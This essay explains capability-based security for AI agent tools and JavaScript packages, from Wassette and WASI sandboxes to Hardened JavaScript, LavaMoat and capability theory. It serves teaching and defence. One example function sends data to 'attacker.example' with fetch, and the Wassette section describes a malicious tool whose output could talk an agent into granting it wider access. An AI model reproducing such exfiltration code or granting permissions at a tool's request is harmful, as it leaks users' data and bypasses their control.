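The WebAssembly System Interface, WASI, is a standard set of such functions, and its designers borrowed from Capsicum. Before the module starts, the host opens a folder and gives the module a handle to it. The handle is again a number in a table that the module can't alter. To open a file, the module gives the handle and a path within the folder, and the runtime (the software that runs the module) refuses any path that leads outside the folder. In effect, the runtime does the job of Dennis and Van Horn's supervisor,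 and the host decides what goes in the list.

k33g (2026), in *One day, one feature*, shows how this works for a small agent program called Mini Me. Users can write tools for it as WebAssembly modules. Each tool gets only the folders that the user opens to it, for reading or writing, and has no access to the network or to environment variables, where programs often keep passwords. The agent can then do useful work without a general tool for running commands. k33g finds this reassuring with small language models, which sometimes invent odd arguments for a tool call. An invented path outside the chosen folders simply fails.

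### Wassette: a sandbox for MCP tools

People usually install an MCP server as an ordinary program on their own computer, where it runs with all their authority. Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* describes an alternative, an MCP server that runs other people's tools as WebAssembly components, which are modules with a standard description of their functions. Wassette exposes those functions to connected agents as tools.

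Each component has its own policy file. If the invoices from the earlier example were saved in a folder, a policy for a tool that reads and pays them might look like this:

```yaml
version: "1.0"
description: "Invoice payment tool"
permissions:
  storage:
    allow:
      - uri: "fs://invoices/**"
        access: ["read"]
  network:
    allow:
      - host: "api.bank.example"
```

Wassette denies access to anything the policy doesn't list. According to an earlier version of Microsoft's documentation, when the agent calls a tool, Wassette finds the component's policy, builds a set of WASI permissions from it, starts the component with only those permissions, runs the requested function and returns the result. With this policy, the tool could not read the customer list or send the invoices to an attacker's server. It could still pay any supplier any amount, because the policy allows access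 to the bank's address and has no entry for payees or amounts.

The network rule is also less like a capability than the folder handles are, because the tool requests a host by name and Wassette checks that name against a list. A tool that serves several people could therefore become a confused deputy.

A user can add a permission to the policy by running a command, but Microsoft recommends asking the agent to do it. The agent then calls one of Wassette's own tools, such as `grant-network-permission`. Microsoft's 2025 announcement of the project gives an example in which GitHub Copilot, a coding assistant, needs to summarise a blog post. The component that fetches web pages has no network access at first, so Copilot prompts the user to allow `opensource.microsoft.com` and then fetches the page.

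In that example, a person can see which site the grant covers and approves it in Copilot's dialog, but a different agent might make the same call without asking for approval. A component's output goes to the model, so a malicious component could return text requesting access to another site. A component's authority therefore includes any access that its output can get the agent to grant. The announcement says that agents sometimes fail to resolve a refused request, and suggests telling them "please fix the permission errors", which invites the agent to grant whatever a component requests.

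Microsoft has since added a way to close this gap. According to its *Releases*, version 0.3.4 of November 2025 introduced a setting that removes all the agent's built-in tools, including those that load components and grant permissions. The user then has to set permissions in advance or with separate commands. This is safer, but it loses the convenience of granting access when a task turns out to need it.

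Wassette also creates a lot of work for tool developers, who must rewrite existing MCP servers as WebAssembly components. Microsoft considers the security worth the effort and is exploring AI tools to help with the conversion. Containers, which package a program with its own files and isolate it from the rest of the machine, require no changes to the code. Microsoft objects that it is hard to tell which web addresses a tool in a container contacts.

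Wassette still looks experimental. Microsoft published six versions between August and November 2025. Version 0.4.0 followed in February 2026 and added detailed logs of tool calls and clearer messages when Wassette blocks a network request. GitPedia's *Wassette*, a copy of the project's front page from June 2026, lists 0.4.0 as the latest version and includes a warning that the software "is not production ready yet". However, Microsoft states in its documentation that Wassette is in use within the company.

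Microsoft also has a newer product, Microsoft Execution Containers, that controls code through the operating system. It became generally available on 7 October 2026, according to CodeReport Global's *Microsoft MXC 1.0* (2026). Developers declare which files, network connections, processes and parts of the user interface an agent's code may use, and the chosen sandbox enforces those limits while the code runs.

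### A sandbox for each request

A fixed policy for each tool is often too coarse. A programmer may want a tool to edit the shell's start-up file just once, or to use the network for an open-source project but not for a client's private code. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (2026), Adam, Lu and colleagues at Brown University propose setting the limits separately for each tool call. They presented the design at EuroMLSys, a workshop on machine learning systems.

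The paper's example is a tool described only as writing text to a file. Its code also sends usage statistics, including the length of the text, to an outside server. The model chooses tools by their descriptions, so this would be hidden from both the model and the user. The proposal has three parts that together expose and limit such behaviour.

The first is static analysis, in which a program examines the tool's code without running it and considers every way the code could execute. It looks for effects, meaning actions on the outside world such as writing a file or contacting a server, and summarizes the results in a short synopsis. For the example tool, the synopsis would record that the path and the text both influence a file write, and that the text also influences a network message.

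The analysis can't determine which file the tool will write to, because the path arrives only when the model makes a call. A check based on the synopsis alone would have to assume the tool might write to any file, and reject it whenever some files are off limits. The second part is therefore a set of small sandboxes inside the tool. For example, the developer replaces each call that writes a file with a version from a sandbox library. This version takes the current request's limits as an extra argument and fails if the path is outside them. Two people can then use the same server at the same time under different limits.

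The third part runs on the user's side, outside the tool and the model. It receives the synopsis when the agent connects to the server. At each tool call, it compares the synopsis with the user's policy and either refuses the call or sends it on with the limits for the sandboxes. Suppose the policy allows writing only inside the workspace folder and forbids network use only on confidential projects. On an open-source project, the example tool would run but could write only in the workspace. On a confidential project, the third part would refuse the call before the tool started, because the synopsis shows a network message that no sandbox controls.

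Developers might forget a sandbox or pass it the wrong limits, so a second round of static analysis checks for these mistakes. It rejects code that has an effect outside a sandbox, unless the policy allows that effect. It also rejects code that might change the limits before they reach the sandbox.

Adam and colleagues built a prototype for tools written in the programming language Rust and tried it on an existing MCP server for programmers. They used three scenarios, each with a harmless version and a version that should fail:

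- The user asks the agent to save a key for an online service in the project folder and add a line to the shell's start-up file. In the bad version, the model guesses the wrong folder for the key.
- The user works on open-source code and confidential code through the same server. In the bad version, the server contains the hidden statistics code, which the team added themselves.
- The agent copies a settings file into a project and later publishes the project on GitHub. In the bad version, the settings file contains a secret key, so two permitted steps together cause a leak.

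The team recorded sessions with two of Anthropic's smaller models, Claude 3.5 Haiku and Claude 4.5 Haiku, and replayed them under four kinds of protection:

| Protection | Harmless versions allowed | Bad versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox with fixed rules around the whole server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Static analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Static analysis with a sandbox for each request | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

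The fixed sandbox blocked the misplaced key, but it also blocked the intended change to the start-up file, because a general rule has to treat such files as dangerous. It did not block the statistics or the published key because it allowed network access. Static analysis alone caught all three problems, but it also blocked every file write in the first scenario. In the third scenario, the full design could hide the settings file from the publishing command, so the rest of the project still reached GitHub.

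Six cases on one server show that the design can make these distinctions, but they give little evidence of how often it would succeed in ordinary use. The prototype also received a correct policy for each request from what the paper calls an oracle. In practice, a person or another language model would have to write that policy and notice that the settings file contained a secret. The experiment did not test this step, which may well be the hardest.

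Tool developers would have to run the analysis, put every relevant effect inside a sandbox, accept the limits as an extra argument and pass them on unchanged. Users would also need evidence that the server is running the analyzed code. Adam and colleagues suggest remote attestation, in which special hardware provides evidence of which program a distant machine is running, but they leave it for later work. Without it, a dishonest server could send the synopsis of a harmless tool and run a different one.

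Rust helped because its strict rules make effects easier to find. Many tool servers use Python or JavaScript, where the same analysis would miss more effects or reject more harmless tools. The analysis covers only the tool's own code, so it can't predict what a shell command or a database will do. For shell commands, the prototype holds all file changes in a temporary area and checks them when the command finishes.

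Access to online services is harder to restrict because the prototype limits network access by domain, and one domain can offer many different actions. When an agent has confidential data, reading a social media post may be harmless but writing one could publish that data, and both requests go to the same domain. Blocking a request can also leave a task partly done. If the sandbox refuses the fourth of five tool calls, the first three have already changed things. Adam and colleagues suggest treating all the calls from one user request as a transaction, which takes effect either completely or not at all. That may be possible for files on the user's own machine, but a payment or a sent email is much harder to undo.

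## How do programming languages use object references to limit, share and withdraw authority?

A sandbox limits a whole program or tool, but most programs contain code from many authors. In most languages, each part can use everything the program can, so a library that formats dates can also read files. Some languages can set limits between the parts by using objects, which combine data with the code that works on it. One object uses another by sending a message along a reference to it. A message is a request to run one of the receiving object's functions. In the object-capability model, these references are capabilities, and objects can affect each other or the outside world only by sending messages along them.

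### Four ways to get a reference

Miller's *Robust Composition* is the main statement of the model. Each object has some code and some stored references. While it handles a message, it can use only its stored references, those that came with the message, and those it obtains by creating objects or receiving replies. Suppose an object called `assistant` is to have a reference to another called `invoices`. There are four ways this can happen:

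- **Initial conditions:** `assistant` already had the reference when the program started.
- **Parenthood:** `assistant` created `invoices`, and a creator always gets the first reference to what it creates.
- **Endowment:** an object with a reference to `invoices` created `assistant` and built the reference into it.
- **Introduction:** an object with references to both sent `assistant` a message that included the reference to `invoices`.

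If no chain of references joins two groups of objects, they can never become connected, because no object can introduce them. Miller summarizes this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". A programmer can therefore bound an untrusted object's authority by tracing references alone. Under the same rules, an object can't leak a capability unless it has another capability that lets it communicate with the recipient, as Habitat Chronicles explains.

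Numbers and text are not capabilities in this model, because any object that can work out a number can have it, even if the number is someone's private key. An object needs a reference to a device, such as a network connection, to affect the outside world.

### What a language has to exclude

Ordinary object-oriented languages come close to this model, but most also let code bypass references. C++ lets a program forge a reference by turning an integer into a pointer. In Java, two objects with no references to each other can communicate if one changes a static variable, which belongs to a whole class of objects, and the other reads it. Reflection, which lets a program inspect its own objects while it runs, can expose their private contents. With unrestricted reflection, code that receives a read-only view of a mailbox could extract the mailbox itself.

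Powerful global variables are another problem. This JavaScript function receives only a number:

```js
function formatAmount(cents) {
  fetch("https://attacker.example/?sum=" + cents);
  return (cents / 100).toFixed(2);
}
```

It can still send the number to a stranger, because `fetch`, which contacts servers, is available to all code.

A single exception like this is enough to break the model. The programmer relies on the untrusted object having no path to the network, but a global `fetch` gives every object such a path, so anyone who traced the references would wrongly conclude that the object can't reach it.

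Some exceptions are hard to notice. All JavaScript arrays share one set of built-in functions, and any code can normally replace them. *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025) gives the example of a guard that uses the built-in function `includes` to check requests against a list. Untrusted code with no reference to the guard or its list could replace `includes` with a function that always returns `true`, and the guard would then approve every request.

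### From W7 to Hardened JavaScript

By 1973, several researchers had noticed that capabilities resemble both objects and the functions of the lambda calculus, a mathematical theory of computation. In the 1990s, Rees built a working system on this idea, described in *A Security Kernel Based on the Lambda-Calculus*. Its core, W7, was the lambda calculus with a few additions, such as changeable data and access to hardware. A procedure in W7 could use only the objects in the environment where it was created and those its caller passed to it.

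In one of the report's examples, Lisa sorts credit card numbers with a program from Bart that might secretly email them to him. If the program's environment contains no way to send mail, the program can still sort the numbers but can't email them. W7 became the basis of Scheme 48, a full version of the programming language Scheme. Scheme 48 ran mobile robots at Cornell with no other operating system.

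Miller's thesis presents E, a language designed for object capabilities from the start. E grew out of work at the company Electric Communities and extends object-capability rules to objects on different machines. Programmers used it to build CapDesk, a desktop designed to be safe from viruses.

Later projects adapted popular languages. Joe-E is a subset of Java that closes the static-variable loophole by allowing static variables to hold only data that can never change. Caja, a Google project that ran from 2007 to 2021, similarly restricted JavaScript so that a web page could include other people's code without giving it control of the page.

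Hardened JavaScript continues this work with three main functions. `lockdown()` freezes the shared built-in functions, so nobody can replace `includes`. `harden()` freezes an object and everything reachable through its properties. `Compartment` creates a separate environment with its own global variables:

```js
lockdown();
const room = new Compartment({
  globals: { invoices, paySupplier },
  __options__: true,
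});
room.evaluate(untrustedCode);
```

The untrusted code can use `invoices`, `paySupplier` and the harmless parts of the language, but `fetch` doesn't exist in its environment. npm, the main public registry of JavaScript packages, has a similar example in which the code receives only a function for printing text. Hardened JavaScript is a proposal to the committee that standardises the language, but developers can already use it through the SES library. According to Socket's catalogue page for the library, *ses*, most existing JavaScript libraries can run on it.

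### Wrappers for the invoice assistant

Suppose the invoice assistant's harness is written in Hardened JavaScript and has two powerful objects, `mailbox` and `bank`. The model can't hold references, but the harness can connect each of the model's tools to a weaker object, which limits what any call to that tool can do.

An attenuating wrapper offers part of what another object can do. This one gives read-only access to a single folder:

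```js
function makeFolderReader(mailbox, folder) {
  return harden({
    list: () => mailbox.list(folder),
    read(id) {
      if (!mailbox.list(folder).includes(id)) throw Error("wrong folder");
      return mailbox.readText(id);
    },
  });
}
const invoices = makeFolderReader(mailbox, "invoices");
```

Code with a reference to `invoices` can list the folder's messages and read their text. It can't send or delete mail, because the wrapper has no functions for that, and it can't read other folders, because `read` checks where each message is. It also can't extract `mailbox`, which is visible only to the code inside `makeFolderReader`. Wrappers can contain other wrappers, so the harness could wrap `invoices` again to show only this month's messages.

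The payment object fixes the payee and the total, with all amounts in cents:

```js
function makePayment(bank, payee, limit) {
  let left = limit;
  return harden({
    pay(amount) {
      if (!Number.isInteger(amount) || amount <= 0 || amount > left) {
        throw Error("refused");
      }
      left -= amount;
      return bank.transfer(payee, amount);
    },
  });
}
const paySupplier = makePayment(bank, supplierAccount, 120000);
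```

The holder of `paySupplier` can pay this supplier up to 1,200 dollars in total, in one or more payments, but can't use it to pay anyone else or see the account balance. The code reduces the allowance before contacting the bank, so a failed transfer may use up some of the allowance but can't lead to overspending.

### Taking authority back

`paySupplier` works until the allowance runs out, but the owner may want to stop payments sooner. A revocable forwarder passes requests on until someone switches it off. Miller calls it a caretaker and credits the idea to work by David Redell in 1974. Miller's version, written in E, forwards any message, while this one is only for payments:

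```js
function makeRevocable(target) {
  let current = target;
  return harden({
    forwarder: {
      pay(amount) {
        if (current === null) throw Error("revoked");
        return current.pay(amount);
      },
    },
    revoke() { current = null; },
  });
}
```

The harness gives the assistant `forwarder` and keeps `revoke`. The assistant can still make payments, but it can't obtain a reference to the object behind the forwarder or prevent the owner from revoking the forwarder. If the assistant passes the forwarder to a helper program, revoking it also stops the helper from making payments through it. The owner can also make a separate forwarder for each assistant and revoke one without affecting the others.

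A forwarder protects only the object it wraps. Suppose the harness puts one around a mail folder, and opening a message returns a reference to an attachment. The assistant could still use that reference after the owner revoked access to the folder. If the attachment had a function that returned the original folder, the assistant could regain access to the whole folder.

A membrane prevents this by wrapping every reference that passes through it. In this simplified version, all capabilities are functions:

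```js
function makeMembrane(target) {
  let enabled = true;
  function wrap(value) {
    if (Object(value) !== value) return value; // text, numbers
    if (typeof value !== "function") throw Error("unsupported");
    return harden((...args) => {
      if (!enabled) throw Error("revoked");
      return wrap(value(...args.map(wrap)));
    });
  }
  return harden({
    wrapped: wrap(target),
    revoke() { enabled = false; },
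  });
}
```

The assistant can use `wrapped` to open a message, use the function it gets back to open an attachment, and so on. When the owner calls `revoke`, all these functions stop working at once. The membrane also wraps what the assistant sends in, so if the assistant gave the mail system a function to call when an invoice arrived, `revoke` would disable that function too. Miller recommends membranes when the owner can't rely on the code on either side, because they separate the two sides even if both try to stay connected.

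Text passes through unwrapped, because revoking access can't take back information the assistant already has. If the assistant has copied an invoice, it can still read the copy after the owner revokes access. The simplified code also doesn't handle thrown errors, which a full membrane must. When a JavaScript function fails, it can throw an error object to its caller, and that object could contain an unwrapped reference.

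### Sealed boxes

Sometimes an object needs to carry something that it shouldn't be able to read or change. A sealer puts a value in a box that only the matching unsealer can open:

```js
function makeSealerPair() {
  const contents = new WeakMap();
  return harden({
    seal(value) {
      const box = harden({});
      contents.set(box, value);
      return box;
    },
    unseal(box) {
      if (!contents.has(box)) throw Error("not our box");
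      return contents.get(box);
    },
  });
}
```

The box is an empty object, and the pair keeps a private table that records what each box stands for. W7 had a similar facility, which Rees compared to digital signatures. No encryption is involved, so the boxes work only inside one running program.

For example, the business might keep a register of suppliers whose account numbers someone has checked. The register has `seal`, and the payment code has `unseal` and accepts only boxes as payees. The assistant receives a box for each supplier and passes the box to the payment code to make a payment. It can't read or alter the account number in a box, or make a box for an account number from an invoice. An attacker therefore can't redirect a payment to a new account by changing the number on an invoice, although the assistant could still use the wrong supplier's box.

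A program can also give everyone `seal` and keep `unseal` to itself. Other objects can then send it secrets through an intermediary that can't read them.

### LavaMoat and malicious packages

JavaScript programs usually load many packages written by strangers. Cornelissen and Balliu cite research finding that the average package on npm depends on 79 others from 40 maintainers. Node.js, the usual way to run JavaScript outside a browser, typically gives all of them the application's full access to the system. Few packages seem to need that much access. In *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System*, Ferreira, Jia and colleagues (2021) observed that many packages perform only simple computations and don't need files or the network.

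LavaMoat uses Hardened JavaScript to limit each package separately. The team behind it works on MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet whose users could lose money to a malicious package. It works as follows:

1. LavaMoat scans the application's packages and writes a policy file that lists which global variables, system functions and other packages each one uses.
2. The developer reviews the policy and can add or remove permissions in a second file.
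3. When the application runs, LavaMoat calls `lockdown()` and loads each package into its own compartment, with only the references in its policy.

LavaMoat's *Using Policies* explains that a grant can cover a single function, such as `fs.readFile`, without the rest of the file system module. LavaMoat also destroys as many of the original global references as it can at the start ("scuttling"), so little remains to use if the application accidentally lets a package reach the real global object. The policy does not apply to the application's own code.

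In September 2025, an attacker published malicious versions of several popular npm packages, including `chalk`. The code looked for cryptocurrency wallets and replaced the recipient's address in transactions with a similar-looking one belonging to the attacker. The security firm OtterSec describes testing LavaMoat against this malware in *How to Survive Supply-Chain Attacks* (2025). It generated a policy for the last harmless version of `chalk`, which needed only two pieces of information about the browser. Under that policy, the malicious version failed when it tried to replace `fetch`, because LavaMoat had frozen the global object.

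That test shows that the mechanism can stop real malware, but it was a reconstruction of the attack, not a defense of a live application. The attackers made only about $1,000 in the first two days. OtterSec had also found ways around LavaMoat's protection when auditing one of LavaMoat's components in late 2024.

LavaMoat protects only applications that use it. MetaMask also publishes a software kit that other developers add to their own websites. According to GitLab's *GHSA-qj3p-xc97-xw74* (2025), developers who installed the kit during a two-and-a-half-hour period on 8 September may also have received a malicious version of the package `debug`.

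Cornelissen and Balliu tested a related tool, NodeShield, on a larger set of attacks. NodeShield limits which other packages a package can load and which of seven groups of system functions, such as file or network access, it can use. It stopped 66 of 67 known malware samples and added less than a millisecond to each server request. Its permissions are coarser than LavaMoat's, so a package allowed to read one file can read any file.

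Those samples came from 46 packages, and 41 of them attacked while the application was running. But Cornelissen and Balliu's full collection had 1,594 packages that attacked during installation, before a tool like LavaMoat's runtime would normally start. *You Can Run But You Can't Hide* (2023), a paper on malicious updates, cites research that found a different balance, with over 40% of attacks on software suppliers starting at runtime.

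An attack in March 2026 shows how installing a package can compromise a computer. *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (Tafani-Dereeper, 2026) reports that an attacker took over a maintainer's account for `axios`, a popular package, and published two versions with a malicious dependency. The dependency downloaded a program that let the attacker control the victim's computer remotely. According to SANS, a security training organisation, organisations were safe if they had locked the version of `axios` they used or had blocked automatic installation scripts. LavaMoat has a separate tool that blocks these scripts unless the developer approves them.

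### What the approach costs

With object capabilities, programmers must pass references that other languages supply automatically. Suppose `main` calls `processInvoices`, which calls `settle`, which calls `recordPayment`. If `recordPayment` later needs to write to a log, all three functions above it may have to handle a reference to the log. This lengthens the code and gives `processInvoices` and `settle` access to a log they don't need. The programmer can avoid some of this by creating `recordPayment` in `main` with the log built in, then passing down only that function. Some languages instead have the compiler track which capabilities each function uses.

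Existing libraries can also be a problem because many use powerful global variables or change the built-in functions. LavaMoat's suggested fix is to patch packages that won't run under its restrictions. Cornelissen and Balliu chose not to freeze the shared built-ins in NodeShield because some harmless packages modify them, for example to add features that an older system lacks. Their tool therefore runs more existing code, but a malicious package can still tamper with built-ins that other packages rely on.

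Wrappers can contain mistakes. Suppose the payment object checked only whether `amount > left`. JavaScript uses the value `NaN` for results that are not numbers, and a `>` comparison with `NaN` is always false. A call to `pay(NaN)` would therefore pass the check and turn the remaining allowance into `NaN`, so every later payment would pass too, however large. The `Number.isInteger` check prevents this, but a programmer could easily leave it out, and the wrapper would still work correctly in ordinary use.

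Developers can make similar mistakes in policies. In LavaMoat, writing `"a": true, "a.b": false` leaves `a.b` accessible, so a user who wants to grant everything in the object `a` except `a.b` has to list the permitted parts instead. OtterSec also warns that if a developer regenerates the policy while a malicious package is installed, the new policy may grant the access the malware needs.

Somebody therefore has to review the policies, and Cornelissen and Balliu tried to measure how much work this takes. With NodeShield, developers had to review less than one new permission per package update on average, and between 0 and 13 for each new package. The reviewer also has to consider what packages can do through each other, because a package without network access might use one that has it as a confused deputy. NodeShield shows the reviewer each package's own permissions together with those of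 every package it depends on, but grants each package only its own at runtime.

A package with permission to start other programs or load machine code can escape the language's rules, because those rules apply only to JavaScript. NodeShield and LavaMoat treat loading machine code as a separate permission, and LavaMoat advises developers to check any such grant carefully.

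## Do capabilities do anything that access lists cannot, and can their spread be controlled?

Researchers had working capability systems by the 1970s, but for decades many people in computer security doubted them. These skeptics believed that capabilities were just access lists stored in a different order, that nobody could control their spread, and that nobody could revoke them. In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller and colleagues refute all three beliefs for systems in which capabilities are object references. Some other capability systems can't control the spread, and access lists have advantages that the paper barely mentions.

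### One matrix, different rules

The argument that access lists and capabilities are equivalent comes from the access matrix. Each access list is a column of the matrix and each capability list is a row, so regrouping the entries converts one form into the other, and both can record the same arrangements of rights. The computer scientist David Wagner has said on record that he thought the two were roughly equal in expressive power until one of the paper's authors argued otherwise.

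Miller and colleagues reply that the matrix shows who has which rights at one moment but not how those rights can change. Two systems with identical matrices could therefore have different ones later. Lampson did propose rules for changing rights, but most people remember only the matrix. On the Unix machine with three files, for example, Bob can read the login notice but Alice can't. With access lists, whoever controls the notice can add Alice to its list, whatever Bob wants. With object capabilities, Bob can give Alice access, but only if he already has a capability for sending messages to her.

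An access list is stored with the resource and names subjects, so whoever edits it must know which subjects exist. That is hard when programs start and stop all the time, so designers tend to use something more stable as the subject, usually a person's account. A capability is stored with the subject and points to the resource, so the system can treat every running program as a separate subject without updating any lists.

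### Seven properties

Miller and colleagues turn these differences into seven properties that a system may or may not have:

- **A. No designation without authority:** anything that identifies a resource also carries the right to use it. A file path fails this test.
- **B. Dynamic subject creation:** a program can create new subjects, for example by starting another program with fewer rights.
- **C. Subject-aggregated authority management:** each subject manages the rights it holds. With access lists, the power to change rights usually belongs to whoever controls the resource.
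- **D. No ambient authority:** a subject has to select the right it is using each time.
- **E. Composability of authorities:** a resource can itself be a subject. A program can then stand in for a file, as a revocable forwarder does.
- **F. Access-controlled delegation channels:** a subject can pass a right to another subject only if it already has access to that subject.
- **G. Dynamic resource creation:** the system can protect resources individually as programs create them.

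They then compare access lists with three meanings of "capabilities": a row of the matrix, a key that its holder can copy and give to anyone, and an object reference, as in Hydra, KeyKOS and E. The last column below is for POSIX "capabilities", a Unix mechanism with a confusing name.

| Property | Access lists | Rows | Keys | Object references | POSIX |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A. No designation without authority | impossible | possible | no | yes | no |
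| B. New subjects | no, in practice | yes, in practice | yes | yes | yes |
| C. Subjects manage rights | no, in practice | yes, in practice | yes | yes | yes |
| D. No ambient authority | no | no | yes | yes | no |
| E. Resources can be subjects | unspecified | unspecified | no | yes | no |
| F. Controlled delegation | unspecified | unspecified | no | yes | through file permissions |
| G. New resources | yes | yes | yes | yes | no |

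The equivalence argument compares the first two columns, but most capability systems that people have built belong in the fourth. Only property A is strictly impossible with access lists. The entries for B and C describe the systems that Miller and colleagues knew of, and a designer could build an access-list system with finer subjects. Android phones, for instance, run each app under a separate user account. Property A is therefore the firmest example of what capabilities add, and it is the one that would have protected Tymshare's billing file. A system with property A also has property D, because every request that identifies a resource includes the right being used.

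The table also helps explain the other two beliefs. Without property F, a holder can pass a right to anyone, and without property E, nobody can build a forwarder to cut off access later. Physical keys lack both properties, so someone who thinks of capabilities as keys will conclude that they spread freely and can't be withdrawn. That conclusion follows from the comparison, which is a useful introduction to capabilities but misleading on these two points.

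POSIX "capabilities" divide the power of a Unix administrator into a fixed set of flags. One of them, `CAP_CHOWN`, lets a program change the owner of any file on the machine. No flag can refer to one particular file, so the mechanism can't by itself limit a program to the files it needs.

### Boebert's argument

The best-known case against capabilities concerns military secrecy. In 1984, Earl Boebert considered a system that assigns every program and every piece of storage to a security level. The system must let a program read only from storage at or below its own level and write only to storage at or above that level. The restriction on writing, known as the star property, stops a program that has read something secret from copying it to a lower level.

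Boebert's example has two levels, with one program and one memory segment at each. A trusted component follows the rules when it hands out capabilities:

| | Low segment | High segment |
|---|---|---|
| Low program | read, write | write |
| High program | read | read, write |

The two programs can then cooperate to break the second rule:

1. The low program takes its capability to write to the low segment and stores a copy of it in that segment.
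2. The high program reads the low segment, as the rules allow, and finds the capability there.
3. The high program reads a secret from the high segment and uses its new capability to write the secret into the low segment.

The low program can now read the secret, even though the trusted component made no mistake. Li Gong cited this argument in 1989 as showing that an ordinary capability system can neither enforce the star property nor confine a program, and others repeated the claim for years.

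The attack depends on its first step, in which a program stores a capability as if it were data. Nearly all capability systems distinguish capabilities from data, and Miller and colleagues use this distinction to repair the example. They split each right to read or write into one for data and one for capabilities. The trusted component hands out both kinds within a level but only the data kind between levels. The low program can still send data up and the high program can still read data from below, but neither can move a capability between levels, so the attack fails at the second step. The repaired system still fits Boebert's definition of an unmodified capability machine, which uses only capabilities to control access to storage.

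Miller and Shapiro give another solution, which needs no special support from the operating system. They put a small program called a data diode between the levels. In JavaScript, it might look like this:

```js
function makeDiode() {
  let value = 0;
  return harden({
    writer: {
      write(n) {
        if (!Number.isInteger(n)) throw Error("integers only");
        value = n;
      },
    },
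    reader: { read: () => value },
  });
}
```

The low program receives `writer` and the high program receives `reader`. Integers can travel up, but nothing can travel down. If the low program tries to send a capability, a check in the diode's code rejects it. An analyst who looked only at which objects are connected, and not at the code, would have to assume that the diode might pass capabilities along, and would wrongly conclude that Boebert was right. Boebert later described the 1984 paper as "no more than an offhand remark" that mattered because it led Richard Kain and Carl Landwehr to write a fuller paper, but that paper supported the same claim by citing Boebert.

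Boebert's result does hold where a capability is only a string of bits. In a password capability system, such as the Amoeba operating system, a capability contains a number too hard to guess, and any program that can send data can send that number. A few systems of this kind have extra defences, but most can't distinguish a capability from other data. The secret web addresses that Close and Tahoe-LAFS recommend have the same weakness, as do the bearer tokens that many online services accept. If a harness shows a language model one of these strings, the model can copy it into an email.

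### Can anyone predict where a right will end up?

The repair to Boebert's example works because the layout is small enough to check by hand. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976) proved in *Protection in Operating Systems* that no algorithm can determine, for every system, whether a right might ever reach the wrong program.

Their model is an access matrix plus a finite set of commands that change it. Each command first tests whether certain rights are present, then adds or deletes rights, or creates or destroys subjects and objects. A simple one might be:

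```text
command share_read(owner, colleague, file):
    if owner has "own" for file
    then add "read" to colleague's entry for file
```

The safety question is whether any sequence of commands could put a particular right in a cell of the access matrix that didn't already contain it. Harrison and colleagues point out that the answer is trivially yes if the owner can give the right away. The analyst therefore has to remove the owner and other trusted subjects from the matrix before asking the question.

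The proof uses Turing machines, which are mathematical models of a computer that reads and writes symbols on an endless tape. Harrison and colleagues showed how to build a protection system that imitates any of these machines. Each square of the tape is represented by a subject that owns the next one. The rights a subject has to itself record the symbol on its square and, if the machine is currently there, the machine's state. Each move of the machine becomes a command, which creates a new subject if the machine moves onto a square it has not used before. The right that represents the final state then appears in the matrix only if the machine reaches that state. An algorithm that could answer every safety question could therefore also determine, for every Turing machine, whether it will ever reach its final state, and no algorithm can do that.

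The result is easy to misread. It doesn't count against capabilities in particular, because the same matrix can represent access lists. It also doesn't mean that every system is unpredictable. Harrison and colleagues gave an algorithm for systems whose commands each perform only one operation. If such a system starts with |S| subjects and |O| objects, and has g kinds of right, a leak that can happen at all can happen after no more than

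g(|S| + 1)(|O| + 1) + 1

commands. With four rights, two subjects and five objects (counting the subjects), that is 73. But these systems are too simple to be realistic, since even creating a file and recording its owner takes two operations. Systems that never create anything are also decidable, although the calculation may take impractically long.

Harrison and colleagues concluded that designers should look at restricted cases. Miller and Shapiro agree, and say the result shows how "depressingly easy" it is to invent rules whose consequences nobody can compute. Some access-list schemes have computable consequences too. For one of the earliest, by Scott Graham and Peter Denning, the safety question can be answered in time proportional to the cube of the input's size.

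### A take-grant example

The take-grant model is a restricted case with a much faster answer. It draws a protection system as a graph, with an arrow from each subject to everything it has rights to. Two of the rights, take and grant, control how the others spread, and the graph can change in only four ways:

- **Take:** if X has the take right to Y, X can copy any right that Y has.
- **Grant:** if X has the grant right to Y, X can give Y any right that X has.
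- **Create:** X can create a new object and have any rights to it.
- **Remove:** X can give up rights.

Suppose a graph has three nodes: the invoice assistant, a helper program and a mail folder. The assistant can read the folder and has the take right to the helper. The helper has no rights.

```text
assistant --read--> folder
assistant --take--> helper
```

The helper looks harmless. It can't take anything from the assistant, and the assistant has no right to grant it anything. But if the two cooperate, the helper can get access to the folder:

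1. The helper creates a box, with the take and grant rights to it.
2. The assistant uses its take right to copy the helper's grant right to the box.
3. The assistant grants the box the right to read the folder.
4. The helper takes that right from the box.

The direction of the original arrow does not matter. If every node is an active subject, a right can reach a new holder exactly when a path of take and grant arrows, pointing either way, connects that holder to a subject that already has it. Passive nodes such as files make the conditions stricter, but Richard Lipton and Lawrence Snyder showed in 1977 that an algorithm can still check those conditions in time proportional to the size of the graph, regardless of how many objects programs might create later.

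In the example, removing the take arrow would permanently separate the helper from the assistant. Each could still create any number of boxes, but neither could reach the other's. The drawback of this quick answer is that it is based on the worst case, so the helper counts as able to read the folder even if the assistant's code would never grant that right to a box. Later versions of the model also cover whether a program can steal a right without its owner's cooperation, and whether information can leak when no right moves.

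### What the EROS proof covers

The practical test of control is the confinement problem, which Lampson posed in 1973. A customer wants to use someone else's program on private data and be sure that the program can't send the data to its author. Miller and Shapiro compare this to buying a pocket calculator from an untrusted company, where the buyer can see that no wires come out of the box.

EROS, the capability system that Shapiro built for Intel processors, does this with the constructor, which *The EROS Constructor* (Shapiro, 2005) describes as the system's basic mechanism for creating processes. Suppose a company sells a program that extracts the sums from invoices. The company gives the constructor the program's code and the capabilities that each new copy will start with. Before running the program, the customer uses the constructor to check whether a new copy would be confined. The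 constructor examines the starting capabilities, not the code. If one of them leads to a network connection or a file that the company can read, the program fails the test. If it passes, the customer can start a copy and give it the invoices, and the copy can send data out only through capabilities that the customer supplies.

A folder that the program can only read might still contain a capability for writing somewhere else. EROS addresses this with "weak" capabilities. According to lecture notes for the University of New South Wales' *Advanced Operating Systems* (2002), any capability that a program reads through a weak one also becomes weak and read-only. The company can therefore include reference data with its program without creating a way for data to leak.

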